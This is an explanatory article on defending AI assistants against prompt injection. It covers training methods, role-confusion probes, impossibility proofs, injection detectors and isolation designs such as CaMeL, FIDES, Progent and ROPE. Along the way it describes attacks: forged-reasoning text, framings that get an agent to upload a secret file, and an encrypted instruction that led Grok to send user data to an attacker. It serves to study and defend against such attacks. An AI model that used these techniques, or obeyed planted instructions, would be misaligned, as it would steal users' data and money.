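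He and colleagues' own system, RETA, trains the model to reason before each action about whether that action follows from the user's request. The model doesn't have to decide whether an email looks like an attack, so rewording the attack should help less. During training, the attacker also earns a reward for using strategies it has not used before. On two small models, none of six adaptive attacks succeeded more than 10% of the time, and the average success rates were 2.92% on one model and 3.75% on the other. For the example assistant, checking actions against the user's request should stop an email that asks for a tax return. It is much less likely to stop a forged invoice, because the user asked the assistant to pay invoices.

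OpenAI acknowledges that a model can look safer simply by refusing more requests. It reports that it tested GPT-5.6, one of the larger models, for this and found the model's normal capabilities unaffected.

### Role confusion

*Prompt Injection as Role Confusion* (Ye, Cui and Hadfield-Menell, 2026), a paper from the International Conference on Machine Learning, makes the strongest argument that training may fall short. It concerns role tags, the markers that separate the parts of the model's context. Different tags introduce the system prompt, the user's words, the model's private reasoning, its answers and the results of tools. Each carries a different authority. The model should obey the user, act on its own reasoning, and treat a tool result only as information.

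An attacker usually can't forge the tags. If someone types one into a message, the provider's software can break it up so the model receives ordinary characters. Ye and colleagues asked whether the genuine tags determine what the model takes a piece of text to be.

To find out, they built role probes, which are simple classifiers that take as input the numbers a model computes internally for each token. In an ordinary conversation, text in a user tag also sounds like a user, so a probe trained on conversations might learn to recognize the style and ignore the tag. The researchers therefore took neutral passages from the web and put a copy of each passage in each of the five tags. Only the tag differed between copies, so the probe could learn only what the tag changed inside the model.

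They then ran the probes on a conversation about gardening with gpt-oss-20b, a small open model from OpenAI. With the correct tags in place, the probe assigned the model's reasoning an average probability of 85% of being reasoning. The figure was 83% when the researchers removed all the tags, and 85% when they put the entire conversation in user tags. Although the probe had learned only the effect of tags, the style of the text produced the same internal signal when the tags were missing or wrong.

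The researchers found the same effect with a mismatch that matters for an email assistant. They put users' messages from 200 real conversations into tool tags and tested four open models. The probes still gave the text a 76% to 88% probability of being the user's, and at most a 20% probability of being a tool result.

They had first noticed the problem through an attack that adds a passage to a user message or web page, written in the style of the model's own reasoning and concluding that the request is permitted. Forgeries with nonsensical justifications worked about as often as plausible ones (60% against 63%), which suggests that the model's compliance did not depend on the quality of the argument. On a benchmark of harmful requests, the attack succeeded about 60% of the time against six OpenAI models that had resisted nearly everything else.

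The researchers then had another model rewrite each forgery, keeping the argument but removing phrases typical of the target's reasoning. The success rate fell from 61% to 10%. The two versions mean much the same thing to a human reader, so the drop is good evidence that the forgeries worked mainly because of their style.

Ordinary prompt injection imitates the user instead. To test this, the researchers wrote 212 framings for the same command, which told an agent to upload a secret file. Some framings stated that the text came from the user. The researchers hid the framed command in web pages and asked the agent to summarize the pages. Over 1,000 attempts, they compared the outcome with how strongly the probe classified the command as the user's words. The attack succeeded 2% of the time in the lowest band of scores and 70% of the time in the highest. Success also rose with the score among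 framings that all claimed to come from the user.

The link between confusion and success is strong but partly correlational. A framing that sounds more like the user might also influence the model in ways the probe does not measure. The probes covered four open models with 20 to 120 billion parameters. Outsiders cannot run a probe on a closed commercial model because it requires access to the model's internal numbers.

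### Is the problem unsolvable?

Slashdot's *A Fundamental Flaw Leaves LLMs Strikingly Vulnerable To Attack* quotes a July 2026 *MIT Technology Review* article in which Ye sees "a real probability" that the problem is "fundamentally unsolvable". The article goes further, describing the paper as arguing that full security is impossible. Willison (2026), in *Prompt Injection as Role Confusion*, also read the paper as confirming that models cannot separate trusted text from untrusted. In 2024 Schneier still expected someone to find a way, but he calls prompt injection "an unsolvable problem" in *Why AI Keeps Falling for Prompt Injection Attacks*.

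The experiments show only that several models, trained in the usual way, identify roles largely by style. The paper lists as an open question how design and training could produce a clean separation. The probes give some reason for hope, because they could not have worked if the tags left no trace inside the model, although style outweighs that trace.

Ye and colleagues argue that more training of the same kind will fall short. They say a model can resist a planted instruction either by identifying that the text comes from a source without authority or by recognizing an attack from its training. They think current models mostly do the second, so each new way of disguising an attack will work until developers train against it.

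OpenAI's results are the best test of this so far. GPT-Red independently discovered the forged-reasoning attack, and OpenAI reports that the attack's success rate fell from over 95% on GPT-5.1 to below 10% on GPT-5.6 Sol. In a later write-up of their paper, Ye and colleagues concede that leading closed models now mostly withstand the attack. They suspect that these models have learned to give less weight to their own reasoning, which would make the reasoning less useful and a poorer guide to what the model will do next. They have not probed these models, so this explanation is a guess.

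GPT-5.6 resisted between half and 89% of the attacks held out of its training. A model that had only memorized attacks should have done badly on these unfamiliar kinds, and one that reliably recognized that tool results have no authority should have resisted nearly all of them, so neither explanation fits well. RETA also suggests a third way to resist, since a model can check an action against the user's request without knowing who wrote the email. But this check depends on the model's judgment, and text that imitates the model's reasoning targets that judgment.

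Impossibility proofs exist, but they cover less than their titles suggest. Pant, Lohani and Kumar (2026), in *On the Inseparability of Instructions and Data in Shared-Embedding Sequence Models*, consider models that turn all text, trusted or not, into the same kind of internal representation. They require a property they call semantic-faithful control, which means that decisions such as whether to call a tool may depend on the meaning of untrusted text but not on its wording or encoding.

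The proof starts from the overlap between trusted and untrusted text. Suppose an observer sees one internal representation and has to guess which kind of text it came from, with both equally likely. The lowest possible error rate is ½(1 − TV), where TV, the total variation distance, is 1 if the two kinds never produce the same representation and 0 if they produce the same ones equally often. At a TV of 0.98, even a perfect observer would be wrong 1% of the time. Next, untrusted text has to influence the model's decisions, or the model could not use it. Finally, the same meaning can take endlessly many forms, and training can cover only some of them. Pant and colleagues conclude that nothing inside such a model can guarantee the property for every input.

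The proof correctly shows that training does not guarantee the right decision on an untested input. But its last step concludes that the decision on that input is wrong, which does not follow. A network trained on a finite set of sums may still add every other pair of numbers correctly, even if the training examples do not guarantee it. The property also differs from resistance to prompt injection, because a model that obeyed every planted instruction, however worded, would satisfy it.

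Bhatt, Munshi and colleagues (2026), in *The Defense Trilemma*, prove something about a different kind of defense, a wrapper that rewrites each prompt before the model reads it. Their theorem says that a wrapper cannot have all three of these properties:

- It is continuous, so similar prompts get similar rewrites.
- It leaves safe prompts unchanged.
- It makes every output safe.

The main argument of the proof gives every prompt a danger score and counts a prompt as safe if its score is below some threshold. A series of safe prompts can get closer and closer to a prompt exactly at the threshold. The wrapper leaves each safe prompt unchanged, so by continuity it must also leave the prompt at the threshold unchanged, even though that prompt is not safe. The researchers checked their proofs with Lean, a program that verifies mathematics, so the logic is sound.

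The theorem's assumptions limit its reach. The proof treats prompts as points in a connected space, with a smooth path from any prompt to any other, but real prompts are strings of separate characters. A filter that simply blocks a suspicious email is not continuous, so the theorem does not apply to it. The theorem also has no bearing on SecAlign or GPT-Red. Bhatt and colleagues say that their result does not rule out training, changes to the model's architecture or human review.

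### Models built to keep the two apart

Pant and colleagues exempt several designs from their theorem. One uses separate encoders for trusted and untrusted text, connected only by a restricted interface. Another stops attention, the mechanism by which one token affects another, from carrying untrusted text into the parts of the model that make decisions. A third leaves decisions about tools to software outside the model.

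ASIDE, a design from 2025, transforms the representation of every data token from the first layer of the model onward. The word "pay" is then represented differently in an email than in the user's request, and an attacker can't change that by rewording the email. This targets the weakness that the role probes exposed, but it is less clear that it solves the problem. Pant and colleagues present ASIDE as the kind of separation their theorem calls for, but they also argue that identifying where text came from does not stop it from influencing decisions. The model would still have to learn to give the transformation more weight than the style of the text, and only testing can show how well it has learned that.

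Stricter separation could give a real guarantee, but the example assistant still has to act on strangers' invoices. The separation would have to let through facts such as the amount due while blocking orders, and a changed account number is a fact that can redirect a payment just as an order could.

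## Screening incoming text with detectors

A detector is a separate model or classifier that checks incoming text for planted instructions and leaves the assistant's main model unchanged. *Passing the Test You Trained On* (Liu, 2026) describes the usual arrangement, in which the software passes every tool result to the detector before copying it into the context. If the detector raises an alarm, the software either drops the text or stops the task and asks a person.

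### What each kind of detector reads

The simplest detector is a small text classifier, such as Meta's Prompt Guard or the academic PIGuard. It scores a piece of text from 0 to 1 for how likely it is to contain an attack, and flags the text if the score is above a chosen threshold. Most of these classifiers have no access to the user's request. Many can process only 512 tokens at a time, so the end of a long email goes unchecked unless the software splits the email into pieces.

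A second kind uses a language model to cut out the suspect passage and keep the rest. *Defending Against Prompt Injection with DataFilter* (2025) describes a model trained to take the user's task and the untrusted text, and reproduce the text without the planted instructions. *PromptArmor* (2025) describes a method that needs no special training. The software prompts an ordinary language model to find any planted instruction, then deletes the part of the email that most closely matches the model's answer. With either method, the user would still get the genuine part of a poisoned invoice. But *Confidently Wrong* (Biswas, 2026) points out that a language model used as a detector also follows instructions, so an attacker can write text to manipulate the detector too.

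Probes, like the role probes described earlier, read the main model's internal numbers. Kale and Vishwanath (2026), in *Prompt-Injection Probes Learn the Conversation, Not Just the Injection*, read them after the model has processed the email, just before it begins its next output. The model computes these numbers anyway, so the probe adds almost no computation. When the probe flags a text, the software usually sends it to a slower second check, such as another language model, rather than blocking it. In *Your Agentic LLMs Secretly Encode Indirect Prompt-Injection Exposure in Hidden States* (2026), the software instead responds to a flag by starting the model's next output with a passage of reasoning.

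Kale and Vishwanath report that Anthropic runs probes on tool results in many of its products. Anthropic says that classifiers in its browser extension scan all untrusted content entering the model's context, and that Claude behaves differently when they flag something.

### Base rates

Suppose one in 100,000 messages contains a planted instruction, and a detector catches 99% of them and raises a false alarm on 1% of harmless messages. These numbers are invented, and the detection rate is generous. Out of 100,000 messages, the detector will almost certainly catch the one attack, but it will also flag about 1,000 harmless messages. An alarm therefore has about a 0.1% chance of being real.

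The result depends on how common attacks are and on the false alarm rate. The detection rate hardly matters, and the table keeps it at 99%.

| Messages with a planted instruction | False alarm rate | False alarms per 100,000 messages | False alarms per attack caught |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1 in 100,000 | 1% | 1,000 | about 1,000 |
| 1 in 100,000 | 0.1% | 100 | about 100 |
| 1 in 100,000 | 0.001% | 1 | about 1 |
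| 1 in 100 | 1% | 990 | 1 |

The hypothetical attack rate is realistic for the web. In *Indirect Prompt Injection in the Wild*, Khodayari, Zhang and colleagues (2026) checked 1.2 billion web addresses and found planted instructions on 11,700 pages, or about one in 100,000. The rate for email may differ, and someone with a determined enemy will face a higher one. Kale and Vishwanath cite research that puts the rate for job applicants' résumés near 1%. For a recruiter using the same detector, about half the alarms would then be real.

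If the user of the example assistant gets 50 messages a day, she will receive 100,000 in five and a half years. A system that blocked mail automatically would stop one attack in that time, but it would also lose a genuine message, sometimes an invoice, every other day. Asking her about each alarm is not much better, because she would probably dismiss the real one after dismissing hundreds of false ones.

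False alarms also add up within a task. If the morning summary covers twelve emails and any alarm stops it, a detector that wrongly flags 1% of harmless emails will stop it on 11% of days (1 − 0.99¹²).

*PromptShield* (2025) draws the same conclusion, that a low false alarm rate matters more than catching every attack. Some detectors come fairly close to a low enough rate. Liu ran fifteen detectors on harmless tool results from two benchmarks of simulated tasks, AgentDojo and τ-bench. The smaller version of Prompt Guard 2 raised no false alarms in 1,872 results. However, a detector with a true false alarm rate of 0.1% would have about a 15% chance of doing the same, and even that rate means 100 false alarms for each attack. On ordinary text, including business emails and web pages, the same classifier flagged 0.3%.

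Other detectors are unusable at their default settings. PIGuard flagged 29.5% of the harmless AgentDojo results, enough to stop 59.8% of the tasks. One flagged result was a bank's confirmation that the user had changed her password, which PIGuard scored as certain to be an attack.

Automatic blocking is unworkable at these rates, but gentler responses are still possible. One is to run a second check on each flagged message, which Kale and Vishwanath assume takes about a second. For the example user's 1,000 false alarms, that adds up to 17 minutes of computing over five and a half years. The software could also withhold a flagged message from the assistant but leave it in her inbox, so that a false alarm only means she has to read the message herself.

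### What detectors learn from their training examples

A detector can mistake a password confirmation for an attack because it learns whatever separates the attacks from the harmless texts in its training data, which may have little to do with who is giving orders to whom. *InjecGuard* (2024) showed that the word "ignore" could be enough to get a harmless sentence flagged. Such a detector might flag a supplier's message that says "please ignore our previous invoice."

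*Defenses Against Prompt Attacks Learn Surface Heuristics* (Li, Yu and colleagues, 2026) tests detectors on harmless prompts containing words that are common in attacks. ProtectAI's classifier flagged 53.9% of them, and Lakera Guard flagged 58.5%. Removing those words lowered the rates to 23.8% and 47.7%, so the words explain more than half of ProtectAI's false alarms but only about a fifth of Lakera Guard's. Prompt Guard 2 flagged far fewer prompts, 11.5% with the words and 1.7% without them.

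The same study found a similar shortcut in models trained with StruQ and SecAlign, the fine-tuning methods described earlier. The researchers put two unrelated, harmless questions in one prompt. A Llama model trained with StruQ refused 6% of the first questions and 90% of the second. Attacks in its training data tended to come late in the prompt, and it had apparently learned to treat any late text as an attack.

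Probes pick up shortcuts too. Kale and Vishwanath found that probes trained in the standard way did almost perfectly on the standard test, but so did a simple formula that used only seven numbers, such as the number of steps taken so far and the length of the latest tool result. When the researchers tested these probes on the same moments from the same tasks without the planted text, the probes still flagged a median of 80% of the harmless cases across six models. They also flagged 98% of harmless notices formatted like the attacks.

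Adding such cases to the training data cut these rates to 17% and 11%. In applications new to the probes, false alarms stayed low, but the retrained probes caught only 58% of attacks written as plain text at the default threshold. In *PIDS-Bench*, Shire and Kim (2026) found a similar limit in text classifiers. Training on harmless look-alikes nearly eliminated false alarms on similar examples but reduced them much less on security-related text collected from public sources. One detector with a near-perfect score on its own test data still flagged about a third of that text.

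### Whole categories of missed attacks

Detection rates vary just as much with the training data. Liu set each detector's threshold so that it flagged 1% of a benchmark's harmless texts. PIGuard then caught 95.1% of the attacks in BIPIA, a benchmark of instructions planted in emails, tables and code, but only 2.1% of those in AgentDojo. PIGuard's training data included more than 1,100 examples from BIPIA, although not the attacks in the test.

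The Horizon-Labs detector, trained on attacks planted in documents and tool results, did best on both AgentDojo and τ-bench, catching 82.2% of the attacks on the first and all of them on the second. But it caught no more than 20% of the BIPIA attacks that tell the assistant to do some unrelated, harmless task, and only PIGuard and the first version of Prompt Guard exceeded that figure.

The cause of this gap is more worrying than the gap itself, since an unrelated, harmless task does little damage. Biswas tested three detectors on harmful-sounding and innocent-sounding instructions, both on their own and inside documents. The detectors reacted to harmful wording, whether or not someone had planted an instruction in a document. They also gave the attacks they missed scores close to zero, so a slightly lower threshold would have caught few of them.

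An attacker can easily write an instruction that sounds innocent. *Beyond Pattern Matching* (2026) reports that its detector caught about 92% of attacks that openly told the model to ignore its instructions, but about 37% of those worded like ordinary requests. The detector caught about 99% of attempts to steal data, because these contained recognizable patterns such as the attacker's web address.

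Better training data cannot entirely solve this problem. Chang, Nikolić and colleagues (2026), in *The Devil is in the Context*, point out that the same instruction can be an attack in one context and a legitimate request in another. "Send the March invoices to our new accountant" is fine if the user's business partner wrote it, but attempted theft if a stranger did, and a classifier that receives only the sentence cannot tell which it is. Access to the user's request should help. Liu gave two general-purpose language models both the request and the tool result, and they caught between 54% and 78% of the attacks in AgentDojo and τ-bench. That is better than many of the small classifiers, but worse than the best ones.

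All of these tests used static attacks, so they probably overstate how well the detectors would do against an attacker who adapts to them.

### Grok and the unreadable instruction

In August 2026 the security firm Adversa AI published an attack on xAI's assistant Grok that uses encryption to hide a planted instruction from scanners. *Zero-click Grok data theft* (2026) explains the mechanism but withholds the exact text of the attack. The attacker puts the encrypted instruction on a web page, together with the key and directions for decrypting it, and the user asks Grok to summarize the page. A scanner that checks the page can't decrypt the instruction, because it classifies text and does not run code, so it finds a string of meaningless characters.

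Grok can run code, however, and it follows the directions. The instruction becomes readable only then, as the output of a program Grok has just run. Adversa AI argues that the model treats such output as more trustworthy than a web page. In the demonstration, Grok then collected the user's name, rough location, subscription tier and everything she had typed in the conversation, and sent it to the attacker inside a web address. It did not warn her or ask for confirmation.

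Adversa AI reported the attack to xAI on June 3. It says xAI acknowledged the report without giving a date for a fix and did not answer follow-up messages sent on August 4 and 10. The attack still worked on August 19, and Ars Technica's *Grok exfiltrates user data when malicious instructions are encrypted* (2026) reported the next day that Grok was still leaking data. xAI does not appear to have announced a fix by early December.

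Adversa AI sells protection for AI agents, and it does not report how often the attack succeeds. The demonstration also doesn't show what scanning Grok had in place, or whether the same instruction would have failed in plain text. It does show that checking a web page on arrival is not enough when the assistant can transform what it reads. A detector that also screened the code tool's output would at least have received the decrypted instruction. The directions for decrypting were readable from the start, but Adversa AI advises treating encrypted text that comes with such directions only as a reason for review, because blocking every encrypted file would stop legitimate work.

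### The case for a detector as one layer

A detector that misses a fifth of attacks still stops the rest, and it is inexpensive. It can be a small classifier that requires no change to the main model. When a new attack appears, the developer can update the detector without retraining the assistant.

Many real attacks are also unsophisticated. Khodayari and colleagues found that most of the instructions planted on the web came from a few recurring templates, and that about 70% of all the planted instructions were in parts of the page that a browser never displays. Detectors are well suited to catching text that thousands of pages share.

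A detector can also catch attacks that fool the main model. *BrowseSafe++* (2026) tested fifteen models separately on carrying out a task on a web page and on judging whether the page contained an attack. In 74% of the cases where a model obeyed a planted instruction, the same model flagged the page when asked to judge it. A separate check is therefore worth having even if it uses the same model, although strong detectors in the study also rejected many harmless pages.

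Anthropic's figures for its browser extension show the benefit of detectors in a product. With 100 attempts in each test environment, Anthropic's internal attacker succeeded 8.0% of the time against the older model Claude Opus 4.5 with no other protection. The first set of safeguards lowered the rate only to 7.6%. Better classifiers and a better response to their alarms lowered it to 1.4% with the same model. Anthropic writes that even 1% "still represents meaningful risk."

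Alarms are also useful as a record of attempted attacks. If a model ignores a planted instruction without reporting it, the user won't know about the attempt. With a log of alarms, a company can see, for example, that forty employees received the same malicious invoice, and warn them or block the sender.

Anyone comparing products should ask for the false alarm rate on the kind of data the assistant handles, and for the share of ordinary tasks that those alarms interrupt. Liu recommends measuring both and checking whether the detector was trained on the benchmark its vendor quotes. What the product does after an alarm matters as much. After a suspicious email, the example assistant could lose its ability to send mail and make payments until the session ends. A false alarm would then delay a payment instead of causing the user to lose an invoice.

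## Designing the system so that a hijacked model can do little

Blocking the assistant from making payments after it receives a suspicious email works only if a detector notices the email. A stricter design treats every email as suspicious and assumes that an attacker may control any model that has read untrusted content. It uses ordinary software to keep that model away from anything it could damage. The software checks where data came from and what the assistant is about to do with it, so rewording a planted instruction helps the attacker much less than it does against a detector. However, someone has to specify which actions are allowed with which data, and some useful requests do not fit any such rule.

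### Two models and a controller

In *The Dual LLM pattern for building AI assistants*, Willison (2023) divides the work between two language models. The privileged model receives the user's request and can use tools, but it never reads untrusted content. The quarantined model reads the untrusted content and has no tools. An ordinary program, the controller, runs the tools and passes data between the two models.

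Suppose the user wants a summary of her latest email. The privileged model requests the email, and the controller fetches it, stores it as VAR1, and gives the privileged model only that name. The privileged model then requests a summary of VAR1. The controller passes the email's text to the quarantined model, stores the summary as VAR2, and shows it to the user when the privileged model requests it. If the email contains an order to forward the mailbox, the quarantined model may well follow it, but it can only write text.

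The privileged model can safely receive some answers because they cannot contain an instruction. For example, if the quarantined model has to choose from a fixed list of labels, such as "invoice" or "newsletter", the controller can check that the answer is on the list before passing it on.

Willison called his own proposal "pretty bad". It is complicated to build, and a single mistake that passes untrusted text to the privileged model defeats it. An attacker could also trick the user, for example with a manipulated summary that persuades her to paste coded text containing her private data into a stranger's website.

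Two years later, *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections* (Beurer-Kellner, Buesser and colleagues, 2025) described six such designs. They share the principle that once a model has taken in untrusted input, that input must not be able to trigger a harmful action. The researchers doubt that a general-purpose agent built on current models can offer reliable guarantees, so each pattern limits what the agent can do.

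| Pattern | How it works | What remains open or lost |
|---|---|---|
| Action selector | The model translates a request into one of a few fixed actions and never receives the results | The assistant cannot use anything it finds |
| Plan, then execute | The model fixes its list of tool calls before it reads untrusted content | Untrusted content can change what goes into the calls, such as the text of an email |
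| Map-reduce | A separate model without tools reads each document and returns a restricted answer, such as yes or no | A malicious document can get itself misclassified |
| Dual LLM | Willison's two models and controller | Untrusted content can corrupt what the quarantined model returns |
| Code, then execute | The privileged model writes a whole program, which calls tools and quarantined models | Untrusted content can corrupt the values the program handles |
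| Context minimization | The software deletes the user's prompt before the model writes its answer | It protects against a malicious prompt, not against malicious data |

One of their case studies is an email and calendar assistant. A fixed plan stops a planted instruction from adding a new action, but the user may have asked for a reply to the attacker's own email. The planted text can then influence what the assistant looks up and get it to hide private data in the reply, using characters that do not show on the screen. The attacker gets the user's data even though the assistant sent only the reply she asked for.

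### CaMeL on one invoice

Google DeepMind's CaMeL, published in 2025, is the best-known attempt to close this gap. In *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks*, Willison (2025) explains the flaw that CaMeL's designers found in his two-model pattern. Suppose a user asks the assistant to send Bob a document, and Bob's address is in some meeting notes. The quarantined model looks up the address, but an attacker who can write in the notes can make it return a different one. The privileged model never reads the address, so it follows the correct plan but sends the document to the attacker's chosen address.

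CaMeL therefore keeps a record of where each value came from and checks that record before every tool call. Suppose the user tells the example assistant to "pay the invoice Bob sent".

1. **The privileged model writes a program.** It has her request and a list of the tools, but not the email. The program, in a restricted version of the language Python, might look like this:

```
email   = find_email(sender="Bob", subject="invoice")
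invoice = ask_quarantined_model("Find the account number and amount due", email)
send_money(recipient=invoice.account, amount=invoice.amount)
```

2. **CaMeL's interpreter runs the first line.** The interpreter is ordinary software that executes the program step by step. It fetches the email and attaches tags, which CaMeL calls capabilities. They record the source of the email and who may read it.
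3. **The quarantined model extracts the details.** It reads the email and fills in two fields, an account number and an amount. If the email also contains an order to forward the mailbox, the model has no tool to do it with. Both values inherit the email's tags.
4. **A policy examines the payment.** The policy is a short function that receives the name of the tool, the values and their tags. It returns "allow" or "deny", with a reason.
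5. **The interpreter acts on the result.** It makes the payment or refuses it, or it asks the user.

The outcome depends on the policy. Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues (2026), in *CaMeLoT*, give a sample rule in temporal logic, a notation for statements about sequences of events:

AG(call_send_money ⇒ ¬(recipient_tainted ∨ amount_tainted))

AG means "at every step of every possible run". The rule forbids any payment whose recipient or amount derives from untrusted content. It would block both a thief's invoice and Bob's genuine one, because in each case the account number and amount come from an email. A more practical policy would accept an amount from an email, up to a limit, but pay only into accounts that the user entered herself. Bob's bill would then go through if she had paid him before, and a planted account number would be rejected.

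CaMeL checks its policies while the program runs, so a long task can fail at its last step. Nikolaou and colleagues' system, CaMeLoT, adds a check before anything runs. It converts the program into a diagram of every path the program could take and searches for one that breaks a rule. With the strict rule above, CaMeLoT would reject the three-line program before the program fetched the email. It would also return the path that broke the rule, so the privileged model could try a different plan. CaMeLoT still has to wait until the program runs to check whether a particular account is on the user's list, because that depends on the actual account number.

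### What CaMeL guarantees

*CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* (Foerster, Blanchard and colleagues, 2026) distinguishes control-flow integrity from data-flow security. Control-flow integrity means that the planner alone determines which tool calls run, in what order and under what conditions. Data-flow security means that untrusted data cannot manipulate the values in those calls or the values that determine which branch runs. Separating the two models provides control-flow integrity, but data-flow security depends entirely on how good the policies are.

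A false account number in a genuine-looking invoice is a data-flow attack. The tags show that the number came from an email, but not whether it belongs to Bob. If the policy accepts account numbers from email, the thief gets paid without planting any instructions.

CaMeL also does not stop text that misleads the user. The quarantined model writes the summary she reads, and an attacker can use that summary to tell her that her account is at risk and give her a number to call. The harm in the test at Bunq was a misleading message of this kind.

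A smaller leak comes from the pattern of a program's actions. For example, a program might open one web page if a contract is signed and another if it is not. No private text leaves the mailbox, but whoever runs the two sites learns whether the contract is signed. *Adaptive Evaluation of Out-of-Band Defenses Against Prompt Injection in LLM Agents* (Narisetty, Kore and colleagues, 2026) reports that CaMeL's designers demonstrated such side channels against their own system.

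Narisetty and colleagues also report that CaMeL completed 77% of the tasks in the AgentDojo benchmark, compared with 84% for an undefended assistant. No attack of the kind it covers succeeded. CaMeL needed about 2.8 times as many tokens, a substantial but not prohibitive increase.

The 77% does not carry over to less predictable work. In *ROPE*, Ma, Xiao and colleagues (2026) tested CaMeL with four models on AgentDyn, a newer benchmark whose tasks require the assistant to change its plan along the way. CaMeL completed none of the tasks with any of the models. Without a defense, GPT-4o-mini, one of the four, completed 46.7%.

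### Three other ways to place the checks

Later systems check different things, and they also differ in who has to write the rules.

| System | What the software checks | Who writes the policy | If the policy is too loose | If it is too strict |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| CaMeL | The origin and permitted readers of each value | The developer or the user, as program code | An attacker's value reaches a real payment or email | The call fails, or the user gets a question |
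| FIDES | Labels for trust and secrecy | The developer, who also has to label the data | Text from an attacker counts as trusted | The assistant can do little after it reads an email |
| Progent | The name of the tool and the details of the call | A language model, from the user's request, plus any fixed rules people add | An attack that fits the rules goes through | The task stops or waits for approval |
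| ROPE | Whether each sensitive value appears in a trusted text | A model drafts defaults that people review, and a model adapts them to each request | An attacker's value passes as trusted | Genuine bills go unpaid |

#### FIDES

Microsoft's FIDES uses information-flow control, a technique from the 1970s in which software labels data and keeps the labels attached wherever the data goes. Like CaMeL, it builds on the two-model pattern, which *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* (2026) describes as a way to keep untrusted data out of the planner's context.

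In *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control*, Costa, Köpf and colleagues (2025) give each piece of data two labels. The integrity label is either trusted or untrusted, and anything derived from untrusted data is untrusted. The confidentiality label is the set of people who may read the data. If the assistant combines two documents, only people who may read both may read the result. For example, combining a document open to {user, accountant, partner} with one open to {user, accountant, lawyer} produces a result open to {user, accountant}.

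The system uses these labels to enforce two rules. A tool call with consequences may run only if trusted data alone led to it, and data may go only to people who are permitted to read it. The second rule limits the damage from a hijacking, because stolen mail cannot go to a stranger, but it does not stop the hijacking by itself. A developer can also require just one of the rules for a given tool. If only the first is required, the user can send a confidential file to somebody new, as long as no untrusted text influenced the decision.

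FIDES plans one step at a time. When a tool result contains untrusted fields, the software hides those fields in variables and lets the planner read the rest. The planner may open a variable, but doing so makes its context untrusted, and the software then blocks consequential calls. To avoid this, the planner can ask a quarantined model a narrow question. Suppose the user wants a calendar entry if any recent email asks for a meeting. The quarantined model answers only yes or no, and a policy may accept this single bit of untrusted influence. A second query extracts the date and names into a variable, which the planner passes to the calendar without reading it. An attacker could create a bogus meeting this way, but could not turn the request into a payment.

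On AgentDojo with GPT-4o, Costa and colleagues counted 152 successful attacks on an ordinary planner and none on FIDES with its policies enabled. This shows that the enforcement works when the data is labeled correctly. The researchers marked as untrusted every field that an attack in the benchmark used, which a company labeling its own data could not do. Narisetty and colleagues note that the deployed form of FIDES treats unlabeled data as trusted.

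The policies also stopped a good deal of legitimate work. With no attack present, an ordinary planner without policies completed 98.8% of the banking tasks and 75.0% of the office tasks, while FIDES completed 52.5% and 59.0%. Part of the shortfall came from the model, since a stronger one, o1, made better use of the hidden variables and raised completion of travel tasks from 41% to 68%. But the policies blocked many of the banking tasks by design, because those tasks told the assistant to read a file and follow its instructions.

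#### Progent

*Progent* (Shi, He and colleagues, 2025) leaves the assistant's model unchanged and adds software that checks each tool call against a set of rules. Each rule names a tool and sets conditions on the details of the call. For example, a rule may permit a chat message only if the recipient is Alice. The software refuses any call that matches no rule.

A language model writes the first set of rules from the user's request, before it reads anything untrusted, and proposes changes as the task goes on. For each change, a solver (a program that works out whether logical statements can be true) compares the calls that the old and new rules would allow. If the new rules allow only calls that the old ones already allowed, the software applies them automatically. If they allow any other calls, the change needs approval. An attacker who fools the model therefore still cannot widen the assistant's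 permissions unnoticed.

In the invoice example, the first policy would probably allow the assistant only to find Bob's email. After reading it, the model would propose allowing a payment to the account in the invoice. The solver would correctly report this as an expansion, but it cannot check whether the account is Bob's. If the user approves a thief's account number, Progent lets the payment through.

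On AgentDojo, Progent lowered the attack success rate from 39.9% to 1.0%, while the assistant completed about as many tasks as before. In this test, Progent automatically accepted every expansion of its policy, to imitate a careless user. The initial policy alone lowered the rate to 2.5%, so most of the protection came from rules that no attacker could have influenced. Only 6% of later changes were expansions, so a user would have had few to approve. AgentDyn was again much harder. Ma and colleagues report that GPT-4o-mini with Progent completed 6.7% of its tasks.

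#### ROPE

ROPE concentrates on the details through which an attacker can do harm, such as the recipient of a payment or the address of a web page. A value for one of these has to appear in a text that the attacker could not have written. Ma and colleagues recognize three such sources:

- the user's own request and account identity
- content from a sender whom the user named, if the platform has verified the sender
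- the user's own records, such as a bank's log of her past payments

Before the task starts, a language model called the router reads the request and selects which sources may supply each value. After that, software checks the values by comparing text, without using a model. It requires a complete match, so a trusted email that mentions notevil.com does not authorize a visit to evil.com.

If the user asks the assistant to pay the invoice Bob sent, Bob becomes a named source. The system then accepts an account number from a verified email from Bob, but not one from a stranger who signs himself "Bob". It would also accept one from a thief who has taken over Bob's mailbox, because the thief's emails come from Bob's address.

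With ROPE, an assistant running GPT-4o-mini completed 36.7% of the AgentDyn tasks, and 0.3% of the attacks succeeded. The undefended assistant completed 46.7% of the tasks. With any other defense in the comparison that had a similarly low attack success rate, the assistant completed at most 18.3%.

ROPE refused a legitimate payment in one task with no attacker. The user had asked the assistant to fetch her electricity bill from a website and pay it, but the supplier's account number appeared only in the bill, and ROPE treats a downloaded document as text that anyone might have written. Across two benchmarks, 51 attacks succeeded. Of these, 23 put a hotel advertisement into the assistant's answer without using a tool, and 21 got the assistant to include something harmful, such as a phishing link, in content it sent somewhere legitimate. In the remaining seven, the user had left a sensitive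 detail entirely to content that an attacker could write.

### The objection that nobody can write the policies

Neil Gong, who studies prompt injection at Duke University, objects that the policies are hard to define. CaMeL's designers concede much of this in a passage that Willison quotes, listing as a drawback that users have to "codify and specify security policies and maintain them". Willison, who has worked on application security for two decades, still finds Amazon's cloud permission system confusing and is "deeply nervous" about asking ordinary users to think about policies. Progent's guarantees depend on correct and complete rules, and *Extending the Formalism and Theoretical Foundations of Cryptography to AI* (2026) similarly calls writing them by hand error-prone.

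One response is to have a language model write the policy for each request. The model can work from the user's words alone, which reduces the risk, but the quality of the policy then depends on the model. Ma and colleagues tested four models as policy writers on 60 tasks. Claude Opus 4.8 loosened two of the default rules, while Gemini 3 Flash loosened 67. When Gemini wrote the policies, the attack success rate rose from 0.3% to 5.8%. The researchers then had the software discard every change that loosened a default. After that, no attack succeeded with any of the models, but the weaker ones completed only 15% to 18% of the tasks.

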